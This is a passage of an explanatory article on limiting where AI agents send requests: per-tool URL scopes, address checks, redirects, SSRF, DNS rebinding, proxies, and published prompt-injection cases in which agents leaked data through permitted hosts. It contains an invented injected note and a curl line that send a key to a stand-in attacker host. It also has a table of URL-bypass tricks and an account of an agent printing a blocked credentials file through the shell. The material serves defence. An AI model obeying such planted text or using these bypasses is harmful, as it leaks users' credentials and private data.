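# Per-tool URL scope, capability tokens and credential leakage in AI agents

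## How an AI agent reaches the network, and what it carries

An AI agent is a language model that works in a loop. The model proposes an action, an ordinary program carries it out and returns the result, and the model then proposes the next action. Agents are used to write software, search the web and answer email. They act through tools, which are functions the model can call through the program, such as one that fetches a web page or files a report. Many tools send requests over a network. Some of those requests carry a credential, which is any secret that proves a right of access, such as a password or an API key (a string that a program sends to an online service to show that it is allowed to use the service).

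An agent can therefore send a request to an address its user never had in mind, and include a credential in it. To prevent this, engineers can give each tool a URL scope, which is the set of web addresses it may use. They can check each action against a list of capabilities, each of which permits one kind of action on a stated set of resources. They can also keep credentials out of the text that the model reads and writes. All three methods depend on how the model and the program around it divide the work.

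Coding agents first appeared around 2023 and came into wide use in early 2025, according to *Inference After Coding Agents* (Gunsilius, Van Dijcke and Wüthrich, 2026). *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026) cites a count of 177,436 agent tools that developers created between November 2024 and February 2026. The count covers only public repositories for the Model Context Protocol, one standard way of connecting tools to models.

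### The agent loop

Engineers call the program around the model the harness. Claude Code and OpenCode are widely used examples, according to *SkVM* (2026), a paper on moving agent skills between models and harnesses. What the model reads at any given step is its context: its instructions, the user's messages and the results of earlier tool calls. One pass of the loop goes like this:

1. The harness sends the model its context, with a description of each tool and the arguments that the tool takes.
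2. The model writes either a final answer or a tool call, which consists of a tool's name and specific arguments.
3. The harness reads the call and runs the function, or refuses to.
4. The harness adds the result to the context and starts again.

Anthropic's *How tool use works*, a guide for developers, states, "The model never runs anything on its own." OpenAI's *Function calling* gives the example of a user who asks about the weather in Paris. The model returns the name of a tool, `get_weather`, with "Paris" as its argument. The developer's code then looks up the weather and sends the result back to the model, which puts it into a sentence.

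Because a tool call is only a request, a limit on it can sit outside the model, in code that applies the limit however the model came to make the call. Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev (2026), in *Authority Is Not a String*, call the harness the natural place to govern an agent's effects because the harness produces them. They add that the check must be able to block a call before it runs, so a hook that only observes calls is not enough.

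It also matters whose computer runs the tool. Anthropic offers some tools, including web search and page fetching, that run on its own servers. The developer's program usually learns what such a tool did only after it has finished, so a check in that program comes too late and the limit has to be enforced on the servers.

The context also accumulates. In Anthropic's version of the loop, each new request contains the original messages, the model's response and the tool results. A credential that ends up in one tool result will be sent to the model again with every later request, unless something removes it.

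### The release agent

In this invented example, a small software company runs a "release agent" that helps prepare each new version of its product. The agent has three tools.

| Tool | Purpose | Network access it needs | Credential it needs |
|---|---|---|---|
| `read_docs` | Fetch a page of documentation | GET requests to addresses under `https://docs.example.com/guide/` | None |
| `post_issue` | File a report in the company's issue tracker | POST requests to one project on `https://api.tracker.example/` | The tracker key |
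| `run_tests` | Run the product's automated tests | None | None |

A URL is a web address. In `https://docs.example.com/guide/install?lang=en`, `https` is the method of connection, `docs.example.com` is the host (the server to contact), `/guide/install` is the path to a page on that server, and `lang=en` is a query, which gives the server extra data to use. A POST request sends data to the server, such as the text of a new issue. A GET request asks for whatever is at the address, but it also sends data, because the path and query go to the server and whoever runs it can read them.

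The tracker key is `trk_live_` followed by random characters. `post_issue` puts it in a header, a line of information sent with the request, and the tracker's server accepts the request if the key is valid, without checking who sent it. The key is therefore a bearer token, a credential that works for whoever holds it. Surapani and colleagues separate authentication, which establishes who is making a request, from authorization, which determines whether they may do what they request. A bearer token combines the two, so the server cannot distinguish a thief who has copied the token from its owner.

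*Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) discusses a model of access rights as keys that their holders can copy and give to anyone. This describes bearer tokens well, except that the model assumes nobody can steal a key from a holder who chooses not to share it. That is not guaranteed for a token held as text in a language model's context.

"Token" has three meanings here, so "credential" is a clearer word when discussing leaks. Language models process text in small pieces called tokens, each a short word or part of one. OpenAI bills developers by these tokens, including those in tool descriptions. An access token is a credential that a service issues to a program so that the program can use the service, often on a user's behalf. A capability token is an unforgeable record of a capability, which its holder can pass on for someone else to check. A service may also issue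 an access token that is a capability token, and the model will read it as a series of text tokens if it enters the context.

In the simplest version of the release agent, nothing enforces the table above. `read_docs` accepts any URL, and the harness fetches it. The company keeps the tracker key in an environment variable, a named value that the operating system passes to the programs it starts. `post_issue` looks the key up there, so the model doesn't need to see it. But the programs that `run_tests` starts inherit the same variable. If a failing test prints its settings, the harness adds that output, including the key, to the context. The model can then copy the key into anything it writes.

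### Prompt injection

The company's documentation accepts edits from outside contributors. One contributor, who owns `collector.example`, adds a paragraph to a page on releases, saying that the tracker has changed its key format and that, before filing issues, automated readers must confirm their key by opening `https://collector.example/check?key=` with the key on the end.

Prompt injection is text planted in something an agent reads, which steers the agent towards actions its user did not ask for. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (2025), David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, traces the term to 2022. He gives the example of a job applicant who hides an instruction in a CV, telling the recruiter's model to approve it for interview. Security specialists call this kind indirect because the attacker never touches the AI system and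 only writes something that the system will later process.

The title's comparison is with SQL injection, an older attack in which someone types database commands into an ordinary form and a careless program runs them. Programmers can prevent this by passing the user's text to the database separately, in a way that guarantees it will never be treated as a command. David C argues that language models offer no equivalent. A model predicts the next piece of text from all the text so far, and has no built-in line between instructions and data. Developers can lower the odds of a successful attack by training models to prioritize their real instructions or by marking outside text as such, but he thinks there is a good chance that nothing will ever bring the odds to zero. That prediction is based on how models work, and a future design could prove it wrong. For now, builders have to plan for a model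 that sometimes follows the wrong instructions.

Bouras and colleagues cite tests by Liu and colleagues in which attacks on commercial coding editors succeeded up to 84% of the time. That is the worst case, not the average, but it is far too high for a system that holds a live key. The attacks don't have to look suspicious. Bouras and colleagues describe a tampered test that prints an official-looking notice that a signing key has changed, with instructions to restore the build by pasting in the new value, which is the attacker's. A filter that searches for dangerous commands or the names of secret files would not catch this notice.

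Outside text reaches a coding agent through routes including project documentation, comments in source code, instruction files that the harness loads automatically, and the output of any command. Even a genuine reply from a reputable company can contain instructions to the agent. *Alibaba Cloud Got Caught Prompt-Injecting AI Agents* (The Hacker News, December 2026) reported such a case. A developer was using Alibaba Cloud's official command-line tool through an AI agent when some of his queries began to return a 7,153-byte block of English text instead of the normal answer. The text contained instructions for the agent to send back information including the computer's login name, its public IP address, the address of the project's code repository, the agent's task and its operating instructions.

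Alibaba Cloud said that this was a countermeasure against suspected automated abuse, triggered by a high rate of requests, and that it would stop returning such prompts. There is no evidence that any agent complied, and the items The Hacker News listed included no passwords or keys. The developer checked where the text came from and found that the connection had a valid certificate for Alibaba Cloud's own domain. A certificate identifies the server, but it doesn't show whether an agent should follow instructions in the server's reply. The release agent faces the same problem, because the planted note is on the company's own documentation site, at the kind of address `read_docs` is meant to fetch.

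### Ambient authority and the confused deputy

The contributor who planted the note cannot read the tracker key or run anything on the company's machine. The agent can do both, so the contributor uses the note to act through the agent. Computer scientists knew about this kind of trick long before language models.

Hardy, in *The Confused Deputy* (1988), tells a story from about eleven years earlier at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Users could run a compiler and name a file to receive its debugging output. The compiler also recorded statistics about its own use in a file in its home directory, so the operators had given it permission to write to any file there. That directory also held the company's billing records. A user learned the billing file's name and gave it to the compiler as the destination for debugging output. The operating system allowed the write because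 the compiler had permission, and the compiler overwrote the billing records.

The user did not have permission to access that file, but the compiler did. The compiler had no way to indicate to the operating system whether it was acting for the user or maintaining the statistics. Hardy called it a confused deputy, meaning a program that someone else tricks into using its own permissions.

Hardy considered having the compiler refuse to write debugging output to its home directory, but some users might have a legitimate reason to put it there. The compiler could also reject the billing file's name, but there were other sensitive files, and someone would have to add each new one to the list. Tymshare added a way for the compiler to declare which authority it was using, but soon found programs that needed more than two authorities. Hardy preferred to give the compiler a capability for the statistics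 file, which would both identify the file and permit writing to it. The compiler would use a separate capability, supplied by the user, for debugging output.

The underlying weakness is what Miller and colleagues call ambient authority, which a program exercises without selecting it. The program has this authority merely because of where it runs, and it can use a resource just by naming it. The release agent's tests need no network, but the process that runs them can open connections anyway, as can any other program on that machine. Restricting the agent to one harmless-looking command does not solve the problem. Bouras and colleagues point out that pytest, a common program for running tests, loads the project's own code, so permission to run the tests is also permission to run whatever code a contributor has put in the project.

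An agent fits Hardy's story closely. The harness has the user's privileges, and the model chooses the names of the resources to use them on. Surapani and colleagues add a complication that Tymshare did not have, which is that an agent also takes in text from the places it contacts. For example, an agent needs permission to read an email inbox, but any stranger can send messages to it.

Unlike an AI agent, Hardy's compiler ran fixed code, and its programmer knew which file was for statistics and which was for the user. Given a way to express that distinction, the compiler would never have confused the two files again. A language model chooses the tool and the argument anew each time, from a context that contains both the user's wishes and a stranger's note. David C calls it an "inherently confusable deputy" and recommends safeguards that follow fixed rules outside the model. Bouras and colleagues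 concede that even with such safeguards in their own system, an injected instruction can still misuse whatever powers the agent legitimately holds. Fixed rules limit the damage, but they must still allow what the agent needs to do its job.

### Where the theft could fail

Six things must happen for the contributor to benefit from the planted note. The model controls only one of them, the decision to follow the note, and ordinary software handles the other five. Preventing any one of the six stops this particular attack.

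- The harness fetches the altered page and adds the note to the context.
- The tracker key gets into the context, in this case through the output of a failed test.
- The model follows the note and writes the key into a call to `read_docs`.
- The harness accepts a call to `read_docs` for an address on `collector.example`.
- The request leaves the company's network with the key still in it.
- The tracker's server accepts the key when the contributor presents it.

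## Restricting each tool to certain web addresses

The note planted in the company's documentation does harm only if the harness accepts a `read_docs` call for an address on `collector.example` and the request then leaves the company's network. A URL scope can stop the theft at either point.

### Approving a tool or approving a request

Many agent systems ask the user to approve one tool at a time. Someone who approves "web search" or "fetch" approves every address the tool can request. Zhang and Pei (2026), in *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data*, built an attack on such systems, using invented user data. They trained a model so that certain ordinary words in a conversation would make it look up the user's stored details, encode them as a string of characters, and put the string in the query of an apparent documentation search. The search went to a server the attacker controlled, and the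 user's approval of the search tool covered the request. Zhang and Pei add that agent interfaces usually shorten the addresses they display, so even an attentive user would probably miss the string.

With a URL scope, the harness checks each request. Some products do this only in part. Claude Code's fetch tool asks for permission once per host, according to *web search*, an unofficial copy of its documentation. A user who approves one page on `docs.example.com` therefore approves every page on that host for the rest of the session. For the release agent, this would include pages outside the guide.

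Zhang and Pei object that a fixed list of sites would ruin a general-purpose search tool, whose value comes from reaching many sources. The objection is fair for a research assistant but has little force against limiting `read_docs`, which needs one directory on one site. It is also a reason to give each tool its own scope, since a list shared by the whole agent has to be as broad as its broadest tool requires.

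### What a scope contains

Each rule in a precise scope specifies the scheme (`https` or `http`), the host, the port, the start of the path, and the request method, such as GET or POST. The port is a number that identifies one program on the server, and 443 is the standard port for `https`.

| Tool | Method | Scheme | Host | Port | Path starts with |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| `read_docs` | GET | `https` | `docs.example.com` | 443 | `/guide/` |
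| `post_issue` | POST | `https` | `api.tracker.example` | 443 | `/projects/release/` |
| `run_tests` | None | None | None | None | None |

All five parts of a request must match the same rule. If the company kept one list of methods and another of hosts for the whole agent, it would permit POST requests to the documentation site and GET requests to the tracker, which no tool needs. The path in the rule must be `/guide/`, with the final slash, because `/guide` would also match `/guide-drafts/`.

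Products differ in what a host entry covers. In Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, `example.com` covers only that host, `*.example.com` covers its subdomains but not the host itself, and `**.example.com` covers both, according to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*. GitHub's *Network Permissions* describes a firewall for agents in which an entry for `github.com` also admits `api.github.com`. Anthropic's *web fetch tool* describes a tool that also includes subdomains automatically. Copying a list from Codex into either of the others therefore permits more hosts, which is a risk if a listed company lets customers publish pages on its subdomains.

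### The check, step by step

Before `read_docs` sends anything, the harness should do the following:

1. Parse the address, which means splitting it into scheme, host, port, path and query. Refuse it if this fails, or if there is a username in front of the host.
2. Put each part into a standard form. Change the host name to lower case, remove any final dot, fill in the default port, write numerical addresses in the usual way, and work out any `..` in the path.
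3. Compare the parts and the method with the tool's scope, and refuse the request unless a single rule matches all of them.
4. Look up the host name to get its IP address, the number that computers use to find each other on a network.
5. Refuse the request if the IP address is internal, meaning that it belongs to the same machine or a private network.
6. Connect to the IP address that passed step 5, without looking up the name again.
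7. If the server answers with a redirect to another address, start again at step 1 with the new address.

The table below shows how the check handles eight requests from `read_docs`. For comparison, the third column shows the result of accepting any address whose text starts with `https://docs.example.com`.

| Address | Where it leads | Text test | Full check |
|---|---|---|---|
| `https://docs.example.com/guide/install?lang=en` | The page the user wants | Accepts | Accepts |
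| `https://collector.example/check?key=trk_live_...` | The attacker's server, with the key | Refuses | Refuses at step 3: wrong host |
| `https://docs.example.com.collector.example/guide/` | A subdomain of `collector.example` | Accepts | Refuses at step 3: wrong host |
| `https://docs.example.com@collector.example/guide/` | `collector.example`, with `docs.example.com` as a username | Accepts | Refuses at step 1: username present |
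| `https://docs.example.com/guide/../admin/export` | `/admin/export` on the documentation server | Accepts | Refuses at step 3, after step 2 has worked out the path |
| `https://2130706433/guide/` | `127.0.0.1`, the agent's own machine | Refuses | Refuses at step 3: wrong host |
| `https://docs.example.com/guide/old`, which redirects to `http://169.254.169.254/` | An internal service on a cloud machine | Accepts | Accepts the first address; refuses the second at step 3 |
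| `https://docs.example.com/guide/install`, when the host name leads to `127.0.0.1` | The agent's own machine | Accepts | Refuses at step 5: internal address |

The text test fails because the start of a web address doesn't show who controls it. Host names read from right to left, so whoever owns `collector.example` can create `docs.example.com.collector.example`. NVD's *CVE-2026-24052 Detail*, an entry in the US government's database of software vulnerabilities, records this flaw in Claude Code versions before 1.0.111, which used a function called `startsWith()` to recognize trusted sites such as `modelcontextprotocol.io`. An attacker could have registered `modelcontextprotocol.io.example.com`, and Claude Code would have sent requests there without asking the user. GitHub rated the flaw 7.1 out of 10 for severity. The entry mentions no actual attack.

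Lengthening the required text to `https://docs.example.com/guide/` blocks the look-alike host and the one hidden behind an `@`, because neither has a slash right after `docs.example.com`. The path with `..` still passes. In a path, `..` means "go up one level", so `/guide/../admin/export` leads to `/admin/export`. An attacker can also write the dots as `%2e%2e`, so step 2 has to decode them before it works out the path.

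The decimal number shows why a list of forbidden addresses is a poor substitute for a scope. An IPv4 address is a 32-bit number, usually written as four smaller numbers. The address `127.0.0.1`, which means "this machine", is 127 × 256³ + 1, or 2,130,706,433. Many programs accept either form, along with `127.1` and `0x7f000001`, so a filter that searches for the text `127.0.0.1` will miss the others. The scope for `read_docs` refuses them all because none is `docs.example.com`. A tool that may visit any public site lacks this protection and depends on steps 2 and 5.

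Anthropic warns about domain names that use lookalike letters from other alphabets, such as `amazon.com` written with a Cyrillic "а". Step 2 should convert such a name to its ASCII form, which starts with `xn--` and can't match the real name. The lookalike can still fool a person who approves a request on screen or pastes the name into the allowlist.

The program that checks an address and the one that connects to it must also interpret the address the same way. Web browsers treat the backslash in `https://collector.example\@docs.example.com/` as a slash, so they connect to `collector.example`. Some older parsers treat everything before the `@` as a username and `docs.example.com` as the host. If the harness checks the address with one of these older parsers and connects with a library that parses it as a browser would, it approves `docs.example.com` but contacts `collector.example`. The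 safest course is for the harness to build a new address from the parts it has checked and pass only that to the library.

### Redirects

A server can answer a request with a redirect, which is a reply containing another address to try. Most web request libraries follow redirects automatically. If the harness checks only the address in the tool call, anyone who can set up a redirect on a permitted page can choose where the next request goes.

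The harness therefore has to turn off automatic redirects and put each new address through the whole check. According to the unofficial documentation, Claude Code comes close to this: when a page redirects to a different host, the fetch tool returns the new address to the model, which has to make a new call. That is enough when permission is granted by host, but a scope that includes a path also requires checking redirects within the same host, such as one from `/guide/old` to `/admin/export`.

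Redirects are more dangerous for `post_issue`, which sends a credential. With some kinds of redirect, the program repeats a POST request at the new address with the same contents. Many libraries drop the standard `Authorization` header when the host changes, but they keep headers with other names, so a tracker key in a custom header would go to the new host. The simplest solution is for `post_issue` to refuse every redirect.

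### Requests to internal addresses

Three of the requests in the table are attempts at server-side request forgery, in which an attacker gets a server to send requests to places the attacker cannot reach. A company's firewall may keep strangers away from its databases and administration pages, but the agent's machine is often inside the firewall. Some programs also accept any request from their own machine without a password. On a rented cloud machine, the address `169.254.169.254` usually leads to a metadata service, which gives programs information about the machine and can give them temporary credentials.

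In the traditional form of the attack, a website lets users enter a web address, perhaps to import a picture, and the attacker enters an internal one. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026), in *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation*, study what happens when a language model writes the address. They built a test application named TicketOracle, in which a model can call tools, and tried five attack scenarios on seven models. Some models were much more susceptible than others, but they trace the weakness to the application, which accepts whatever address the model produces without checking it. A company that relies on a resistant model would have to test again whenever it changed models, whereas step 5 works the same way with any model.

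Step 5 needs a list of internal ranges. Earl's *Hardening*, a security guide for a program that calls web services, includes these among the ranges that Earl blocks by default:

| Range | Use |
|---|---|
| `127.0.0.0/8` | The same machine |
| `10.0.0.0/8` | Private networks |
| `172.16.0.0/12` | Private networks |
| `192.168.0.0/16` | Private networks |
| `169.254.0.0/16` | The local network link, including the cloud metadata address |

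The number after the slash is how many of the address's 32 bits are fixed, so `10.0.0.0/8` covers every address that begins with 10. IPv6, a newer system with longer addresses, has its own internal ranges, and a complete list needs those too.

Sometimes an agent has a good reason to use an internal service. If the release agent's tracker ran on the company's own network, step 5 would block it. OpenShell, NVIDIA's open-source system for running agents in closed environments, lets an exact host name in the policy lead to a private address. It never allows access to the agent's own machine or the metadata address, whatever the policy contains, according to NVIDIA's *OpenShell Security Best Practices for Controls, Risks, and Configuration Guidance*. Codex is stricter about names. According to OpenAI's *Permissions*, it blocks a permitted host name that leads to a private address unless the user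 also changes a general setting for local networks. This protects users who don't know where a name leads, but changing the setting removes that protection for every permitted name at once.

### DNS rebinding

DNS is the internet's directory, which programs use to turn a host name into an IP address. The owner of a domain decides what answers DNS gives for it and how long other computers should remember them. In an attack known as DNS rebinding, the owner changes the answer between the check and the connection. Suppose that another of the company's agents has a tool that may visit any public site:

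1. The tool asks for a page on `pages.collector.example`.
2. The harness looks up the name, gets a public IP address and approves the request.
3. The library that makes the connection looks up the name again. This time the attacker's DNS server answers `169.254.169.254`.
4. The library connects to the metadata service, and the harness puts the reply in the agent's context.

Step 6 of the check prevents this because there is no second lookup. The harness still has to give the library the original host name so that the library can verify the server's certificate. The check and the connection often happen in separate programs, which makes it difficult to pass the approved IP address from one to the other. Vaughan writes in *Codex CLI Network Proxy*, an outside guide, that Codex's check on resolved addresses prevents rebinding. OpenAI, however, describes the check as "best-effort", says that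 it reduces the risk without eliminating it, and advises anyone who expects hostile DNS servers to add controls at a lower level of the network.

Rebinding is a smaller danger for `read_docs`. The attacker would need to control the DNS records for `docs.example.com`, which belong to the company. The scope also requires `https`, and an internal service would normally have no valid certificate for that name, so the connection would fail before the tool sent its request. A broad scope, or one that permits plain `http`, loses these protections.

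### Where to enforce the scope

An enforcement point is the component that checks a request against the permissions and allows or refuses it. The company could put one in each tool's code, in the harness, or in an egress proxy, a program that all outgoing traffic must pass through.

A check in the tool's own code can use the most information, because that code handles the complete address before encryption and can follow redirects one at a time. But every tool's author has to write the check correctly, and it covers only requests that go through that code.

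The harness can identify which tool the model has called and apply one well-tested check to every tool, but it can inspect only the call's arguments. If `post_issue` takes only a title and a description, the call contains no address, so the harness has to rely on the tool to contact the right server. It also has to rely on the tool to handle redirects correctly, unless the harness makes the web requests itself.

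A proxy covers every program on the machine, including programs that the tools start, if they have no other way to reach the network. To use `https` through a proxy, a program first sends it the host and port it wants. The proxy then opens a connection and relays the encrypted traffic. It can refuse `collector.example`, but without decrypting the traffic it can't distinguish `/guide/install` from `/admin/export`, or a GET request from a POST.

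A program can also get past the proxy because many websites share servers. It can name a permitted site to the proxy and then, inside the encrypted connection, ask the server for a different site.

To enforce a complete scope, the proxy has to decrypt the traffic. It presents its own certificate to the program, reads and checks the request, then encrypts it again for the real server. This works only if the programs on the machine trust the proxy's certificate. It fails for a program that must prove its identity to the server with its own certificate, because the proxy now makes the connection to the server. It also makes the proxy an attractive target, since every credential sent through it is briefly readable there.

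| Enforcement point | Knows which tool is calling | Can check the path and method under `https` | Covers programs that a tool starts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tool's code | Yes | Yes | No |
| Harness | Yes | Only if they are in the call, or the harness sends the request | No |
| Proxy that leaves encryption closed | Not by itself | No | Yes |
| Proxy that opens encryption | Not by itself | Yes | Yes |

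No row in the table has every property. A proxy that receives a request from the release agent's machine can't distinguish `read_docs` from `run_tests` unless the company runs the tools separately or gives the proxy another way to identify them.

### Three systems in use

OpenAI's shell tool lets a model run commands on a computer that OpenAI hosts. According to OpenAI's *Shell*, these computers have no outgoing network access by default. To allow it, an administrator first sets up a list of permitted domains for the organization, and the developer then includes a second list, `allowed_domains`, in the request that starts the computer. The request fails if the developer's list contains a domain that isn't on the organization's. A developer can therefore narrow the organization's list but not widen it, and a mistake causes an error at the start instead of halfway through a task. The same settings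 can attach a credential to a domain without revealing the credential to the model. The lists contain only domains, so they can't restrict a command to the path `/guide/` or to GET requests.

Codex has finer controls for commands on a user's own machine. Network access is off by default, and a user who turns it on without also turning on the proxy gets unrestricted access. With the proxy on, an empty allowlist permits no hosts, and a rule that denies a host overrides any rule that allows it.

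The proxy's manual, *codex-network-proxy*, also describes a "limited" mode that permits only GET, HEAD and OPTIONS requests, which programs normally use to read data. A HEAD request asks for a page's headers, and an OPTIONS request asks which methods a server accepts. Because the proxy cannot read the method of an encrypted request, it refuses `https` connections in this mode unless the user lets it decrypt them. It also turns off SOCKS5, a general way of relaying traffic, for the same reason. OpenAI's *Agent internet access* offers the same limit for the version of Codex that runs on OpenAI's servers. The limit prevents most direct changes to outside systems, but a GET request can still carry a stolen key in its address.

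The user can add rules for a host that specify methods and path prefixes. The manual's example matches POST and PUT requests to `api.github.com` under `/repos/openai/`. The proxy then blocks any encrypted request to that host that matches none of its rules. These rules give nearly the full five-part scope.

Software built around the proxy can supply a function that approves hosts missing from the allowlist, but this feature needs care because it can bring back approval by tool. In the manual's example, the function approves any request from a command that starts with `curl `, a common program for fetching web addresses. A user who approved `curl` for one site would therefore let it reach every site except local addresses and those the proxy explicitly denies.

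OpenShell addresses the proxy's difficulty in telling tools apart. Each entry in its policy pairs destinations with the programs that may contact them, and as NVIDIA's *Customize Sandbox Policies* explains, a connection needs both to match within the same entry. If each of the release agent's tools is a separate program, the entry for `read_docs` could look like this:

```yaml
network_policies:
  read_docs:
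    name: read_docs
    endpoints:
      - host: docs.example.com
        port: 443
        protocol: rest
        enforcement: enforce
        rules:
          - allow:
              method: GET
              path: "/guide/**"
    binaries:
      - path: /opt/agent/read_docs
```

OpenShell identifies a program by its location and by a hash, a short value computed from the file's contents. It records the hash the first time the program runs and denies access if the hash later changes, so an agent can't replace `read_docs` with a different program under the same name. But a program also gets access if any program in the chain that started it is on the list. If the company listed the harness, every tool the harness started would inherit its access. Listing a general program such as Python would be almost as bad, because all three tools might use it.

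Two lines in the entry are easy to leave out. Without `protocol: rest`, OpenShell checks the host, port and program but allows every path and method. By default, it still decrypts traffic and checks that the host in each web request matches the permitted destination, which catches a program that asks a shared server for a different site. Without `enforcement: enforce`, it records violations of the path and method rules but still forwards the requests. NVIDIA recommends starting in that mode to find out whether the rules fit, then switching to `enforce`.

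OpenShell also lets a person approve a blocked destination while the agent runs. The approval lasts until someone destroys the agent's environment, so one hasty decision can widen the agent's access for weeks.

### Why a shell tool needs a limit on the network

Suppose the company gives the release agent a fourth tool, which runs any command the model writes. The scope of `read_docs` is then of little use, because the model can write `curl https://collector.example/check?key=...` instead of calling `read_docs`.

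The company could tell the harness to refuse commands that contain `curl` or mention unfamiliar hosts. Claude Code supports such rules. According to Anthropic, it checks rules that deny a call first, then rules that require confirmation, then rules that allow it, and applies the first one that matches. However, Anthropic points out that a rule against a command applies to the command as written, and the same command can be written in many ways. The model can put the address in a variable, split it into pieces, or use Python instead of `curl`. It can also save a script in one step and run it in the next, so the second command contains only a file name. For limits that don't depend on the wording, Anthropic directs users to the network isolation in Claude Code's sandbox, a closed environment for running commands.

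The release agent has this problem even without a fourth tool, because `run_tests` runs whatever code contributors have put in the project. The scope for `run_tests` is empty, but a check on tool calls can't enforce that, since the call contains no web address to check. The operating system or the network has to block any connection the tests try to open.

A proxy alone may not be enough here, because programs usually get proxy settings from environment variables and can ignore them. When OpenShell runs an agent in Docker, a common system for isolating programs, it disables networking for the agent's container and leaves only a private channel to the component that checks requests. A test that ignores the proxy settings then has no connection.

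Limits on the shell don't automatically extend to other tools. OpenAI states that permission profiles in Codex govern commands on the user's machine, while browser tools and Model Context Protocol servers have separate controls. Requests from tools that run on Anthropic's servers never pass through the customer's proxy, so the customer has to set the limit in the tool's own options. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* recommends that developers worried about exfiltration either use the tool's `allowed_domains` setting or turn the tool off.

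## How data leaves through permitted addresses

A URL scope limits where a request may go but does not fully limit what the request may contain, and an outsider can sometimes read what a permitted host receives.

The query is the most obvious place to put stolen data. A call to `https://docs.example.com/guide/install?lang=trk_live_...` passes every step of the check on `read_docs`, because the scope has no rule for queries. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out that websites commonly log the addresses that programs request. The key would then end up in the documentation site's logs. A path can also hold data, as can the body of a POST request, such as the text of a new issue. The choice of address can reveal information even when no address contains a secret. If an agent opens one page when it has found a password and a different page when it hasn't,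 anyone who can see requests to the server learns which happened.

The harm from a leak to a permitted address depends on who can read the data that arrives there. If only the company's staff can read the documentation site's logs, a key in those logs needs to be cleaned up but hasn't yet been stolen. If the tracker's project is public, anyone can read a new issue. In *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, Simon Willison calls it "a tricky proposition" to find domains that an attacker can't use to receive data.

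### A permitted host that stores data for strangers

Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, runs commands in a virtual machine on the user's computer. A proxy lets those commands reach only certain hosts, including `api.anthropic.com`, because Cowork can't work without Anthropic's service. That service also stores files for its customers.

In January 2026, two days after Anthropic released Cowork, the security company PromptArmor published an attack on it in *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files*. Hidden text in a document makes Claude upload one of the user's files to Anthropic's file service, using an API key that the attacker put in the document. The file goes into the attacker's account, and nobody asks the user for approval. PromptArmor demonstrated this on Claude Haiku, a small model, and got a similar attack to work on Opus 4.5, which resists injection better.

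Security researcher Johann Rehberger had described the same route in October 2025, in Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate*. His attack targeted an older Claude feature for running code and could upload up to 30 megabytes at a time to the file service. Anthropic closed his report within an hour as out of scope, then confirmed five days later that it should have accepted the report. Oasis Security's *Claude.ai Prompt Injection to Data Exfiltration* describes an attack that used the file service to take data from an ordinary Claude chat.

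The credential in these attacks belonged to the attacker, so hiding the user's keys would not have helped. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* reports that Cowork's proxy worked as designed, letting the request through because its destination was on the allowlist. Anthropic now thinks of each allowlist entry as a grant of capability covering every function the host offers.

To fix the problem, Anthropic added a proxy inside the virtual machine that decrypts traffic to Anthropic's API. It passes only requests that carry the access token issued to that machine for the session, so it rejects an attacker's key. It also blocks headers that would make Anthropic's servers fetch something themselves. The check has to run inside the virtual machine because Anthropic's servers can't tell Cowork's requests apart from those of other customers. Rehberger had suggested much the same limit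 in October, under which code run by Claude could reach only the logged-in user's account.

The release agent's `post_issue` already has some protection of this kind. Its code supplies the company's key, so injected text can't switch to another account. A tool that let the model write the request headers wouldn't have this protection.

Attackers could similarly exploit Google's services in Superhuman, an email program with an AI assistant. Superhuman used a Content Security Policy, a list that a website sends to the browser to limit where the page may load images and other material from. The list included `docs.google.com`, which also hosts Google Forms. The owner of a form can make a link that contains an answer, and opening the link submits that answer.

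PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* explains how an attacker could combine the two. The attacker sends the user an email with hidden instructions. When the user asks for a summary of recent mail, the assistant copies other emails into a link to the attacker's form and presents the link as the address of an image. The browser tries to load the image and so submits the form. In one response, PromptArmor obtained parts of more than 40 emails. Superhuman turned off the vulnerable features on 8 December 2025, three days after the first report, and released further fixes until 11 January 2026. PromptArmor's *Codex for Everything Exfiltrates Connected Data* describes the same trick in OpenAI's Codex. PromptArmor reported the flaw in April 2026, and OpenAI has since fixed it.

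Permitting only GET requests would not have prevented this, because loading an image is a GET request and Google Forms stores data submitted that way. A rule that included the path could have blocked forms while still permitting documents on the same host.

Antigravity, Google's coding agent, had a more obvious flaw, because its browser's default allowlist included `webhook.site`, where anyone can create an address and read the requests sent to it. In PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data*, a tampered programming guide makes the agent collect cloud credentials from the user's project and open a `webhook.site` address with the credentials in the query string. The agent's file reader blocks access to the file that holds the credentials, so the agent prints the file with a shell command.

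PromptArmor did not report this to Google privately, because Google already warned users about the risk when they set up the program. In November 2025, Willison noted that Google listed data theft through prompt injection among the known issues it was working to fix. Anyone reviewing the allowlist could have spotted `webhook.site`, which exists to show people the requests sent to it. They would have needed to know how Google Forms handles links to spot the danger in `docs.google.com`.

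### A permitted domain that someone else can buy

An allowlist entry can also become dangerous without any change to the list. Salesforce's customer-management software lets companies put a form on their websites where anyone can enter their details as a potential customer, or "lead". Researchers at Noma Security put instructions in such a form. When an employee asked Agentforce, Salesforce's AI agent, about that lead, the agent collected the email addresses of other leads and wrote them into the address of an image.

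Salesforce's Content Security Policy, which should have stopped the browser from loading the image, still allowed `my-salesforce-cms.com`, a domain whose registration had expired. According to Hackread's *ForcedLeak Flaw in Salesforce Agentforce AI Agent Exposed CRM Data*, the domain was on sale for $5. Noma registered it and received the data. Salesforce Ben quotes Noma as saying that the theft "would have been impossible" without a way around the policy.

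Noma told Salesforce about ForcedLeak on 28 July 2025, and Salesforce had fixes in place by 8 September. The Hacker News' *Salesforce Patches Critical ForcedLeak* (2025) reports that Salesforce took back the domain and stopped its agents from sending output to addresses outside a list of trusted URLs. The second fix is another allowlist, so someone still has to check who owns its domains. That is easy for the release agent, which needs only two hosts. For a list of several hundred, an expiry date on each entry would at least force someone to review it.

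### When the display makes the request

In the Superhuman and Salesforce attacks, the agent only wrote an address. The user's browser then sent the request in order to display an image. Neither an egress proxy on the agent's machine nor a check on tool calls would have detected the request.

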